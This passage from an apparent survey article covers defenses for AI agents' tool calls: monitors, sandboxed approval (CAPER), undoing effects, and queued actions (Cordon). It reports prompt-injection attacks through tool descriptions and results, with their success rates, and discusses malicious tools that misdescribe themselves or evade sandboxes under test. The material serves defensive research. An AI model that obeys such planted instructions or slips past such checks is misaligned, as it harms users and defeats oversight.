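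The researchers acknowledge that the monitor detects a violation only after it has happened. If a weather site's tool reported cities to an analytics service, the service would receive the first city before the monitor detected the violation. The monitor may also attribute a page change to the wrong tool when several things happen at once.

One proposed example of a violation is a read-only tool that makes a network request. But a rule against all such requests would flag an accurately described weather tool, which has to make a request to get the forecast. The browser would need a list of the addresses the tool is supposed to contact, and WebMCP has no label for that.

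Most of the published results concern other parts of the system. The browser gives each script a credential for the tools it registers, which prevents other scripts from replacing or removing them. This reduced successful attacks from 20 in 20 attempts to none. A second model without permission to call tools reads the text first to stop planted instructions. Instructions in tool descriptions succeeded in 69 of 80 attempts without any defense and in none with the full system. For instructions in tool results, the figures were 42 and 2.

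The trust labels had no effect on their own, and 71 of 80 attacks through tool descriptions succeeded. Any script on the page can register a tool and get a valid credential, so the labels marked the malicious tools as trustworthy. The defenses didn't seem to reduce the number of completed tasks much. Agents completed 56 of 80 tasks under attack with the full system, compared with 61 of 80 when there was no attack, a difference that could easily be chance.

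### Running a tool on a copy

A host can prevent the first harm by running the tool on a copy of the user's files and deciding afterwards whether to keep the result. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) presents CAPER, a system that does this for coding agents' shell commands.

1. CAPER saves a snapshot of the container in which the agent works.
2. It runs the command there with the network switched off, and holds back the output.
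3. It produces a short report of changed files, attempted connections and any secrets that the command read.
4. A language model compares the report with the user's request.
5. If the model approves, CAPER keeps the changes and passes the output to the agent. Otherwise it restores the snapshot and gives the agent the reason.

The researchers tested CAPER on 102 tasks in which an ordinary-looking tool secretly deletes or overwrites a file. Each task has a safe version with the same request and command but harmless code in the tool. An approver that sees only the request and command can't tell the two versions apart.

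| What the approving model sees | Dangerous tasks that ended in harm | Safe twins wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| There is no approval step | 71.6% | None |
| The conversation and command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus a model's prediction of the effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus the observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Predicting the effects prevented about as much harm as observing them, but the approver still blocked most of the harmless tools. The main advantage of observation is that it shows when a provider is honest. In one dangerous task, a deployment tool also replaced a source file with a one-line comment. CAPER reported the change, the approver blocked the command, and the agent finished the task by copying the files itself.

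The approval step took a median of 3.2 seconds, about the same as without the report. The sandbox added roughly half a second to each approved command and 1.5 seconds to each blocked one. The time added by copying can vary widely between systems. *Planarian* (2026) reports that taking a snapshot after every tool call added 1 per cent to the time for system administration tasks, compared with 20 per cent for a method that saves full snapshots. *Fault-Tolerant Sandboxing for AI Coding Agents* (2025) reports an increase of 14.5 per cent, or about 1.8 seconds per operation.

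CAPER would catch the weather tool's change to the profile file, and its report would list both attempted connections. With the network off, though, the tool could not get a forecast. If the host let the tool contact the weather company, the forecast would arrive, but the company would have the query even if the host then discarded the copy.

### Undoing a call

If a tool has already run on the real files, the host may still be able to reverse its effects. Waghmare and Sufi (2026), in *Can You Undo It?*, set three conditions for fully restoring the earlier state: a complete record of that state must exist, the user or agent must have the authority to restore it, and no outside party can have seen or acted on the change. The weather tool's profile file can meet all three if the host saved a copy first, but the report to the analytics service can't, because the service has already received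 it.

Waghmare and Sufi sort tools into five classes and applied them to 536 tools on 20 MCP servers.

| Class | Example | Tools |
|---|---|---|
| No effect | Reading a database record | 333 |
| Restorable | Editing a private file after saving a copy | 31 |
| Reversible at a known cost | Placing an order that the shop will cancel for a fixed fee | 18 |
| Hard to recover | Changing who has access to an account | 39 |
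| Irreversible | Sending an email to a customer | 115 |

The researchers prepared these draft counts with AI assistance. Sufi reviewed a sample, also with AI assistance, and 75 of his 148 ratings matched the draft while 67 were stricter, so the table may undercount irreversible tools.

The classes also assume that a tool does what it is supposed to do. Someone who relied on the weather tool's description would put it in the "no effect" class, and the host would not save any copies. This is a good reason to save copies by default, at least of files that an unfamiliar tool can write to.

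Restoring a file can do damage. In eight test cases, somebody else had edited a file after the agent did, and restoring the saved copy erased their work every time. Restoring a file only if nobody else had edited it after the agent did protected the later work, but left the agent's edit for a person to remove. Restoring files may also not be enough for programs that are still running. *DeltaBox* (2026) explains that a program can keep information in memory that no longer matches the restored files.

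Undoing changes also depends on someone noticing the problem. YoloFS, the system in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), holds an agent's file changes in a staging area. When Wu and colleagues tested it on their 102 dangerous tasks, the agent saw a summary of its changes after each command and could reverse them. About 3 of the 66 runs in which it reversed changes ended in harm, compared with 33 of the 36 in which it reversed nothing.

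For payments, the best available remedy is usually a second action that compensates for the first, such as a refund. *POLAR* (2026) describes an earlier system, SagaLLM, that plans a compensating action for each step in advance and runs these actions in reverse order if the task fails. But the refund tool usually comes from the same shop as the purchase tool, so a shop that misdescribed one could misdescribe the other. Even a refund that works as described may leave the shopper with a fee or a delay.

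A host could ask the user before making any call whose effects it couldn't simply undo, but this would interrupt her often. Waghmare and Sufi applied such a policy to recorded runs in which nobody attacked the agent. In 651 of the 770 runs that completed their task, the host would have asked the user at least once.

### Delaying messages and payments

Nobody can recall a sent message, so it may be better to hold it back until the host has checked the whole task. Chen, Dong and colleagues (2026) built *Cordon*, a system that makes file changes on a copy and queues outgoing actions. When the task is ready, Cordon checks everything together, then releases or cancels the queued actions.

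Examining calls together can reveal problems that no single call does. In the researchers' example, an agent investigating a fault reads logs that contain a secret key, summarizes them, and prepares a message to a team channel. Each step is routine, but the message may carry information derived from the key. Cordon tracks which results the agent used in each message, so it can hold this one back.

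In 45 test workflows, an unprotected agent carried out the harmful action every time. Cordon prevented it in all 45, while versions of existing defenses prevented it in 14. The researchers built the workflows around five kinds of risk that Cordon's rules address, so it would probably do less well on risks they hadn't planned for. Cordon took a median of about 4 milliseconds to discard unwanted local changes.

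Cordon needs a declaration of what each tool reads, writes and sends, but that declaration can misrepresent the tool just as its description can. If a shop declared that "finalizeCart" only reads, a host that trusted the declaration would have no reason to queue the call. The host could hold back every call to an unfamiliar shop, but once it released this one, the shop's server would determine whether the call displayed the cart or bought its contents.

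Delay also suits some tools better than others. An agent can usually keep working while an email waits in a queue, but it can't report the weather in Lisbon until the request has gone out, and that request discloses the user's interest in Lisbon.

### Tools that behave differently under test

A tool that behaves well for a directory's reviewers can do the same in a sandbox, for example by skipping the analytics report when the home folder is empty. Wu and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker might detect CAPER's sandbox or delay the harm, but neither of their sets of test tasks includes such an attacker.

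It helps if the host observes the same run whose result it keeps. CAPER runs each command only once and keeps the result if the model approves it. If the weather tool does not change the profile file during that run, the file is unchanged when the result is kept. The tool could still leave behind a script that changes the file later, when another program runs it outside the sandbox.

An enforced permission list works better against this kind of deception because it doesn't depend on detecting misbehavior. A weather tool that has made only the expected connections for 300 calls still can't contact `stats.example` on call 301. To get around the list, the provider would have to send the extra data through `api.weather.example`, which the list must allow for the user to get a forecast.
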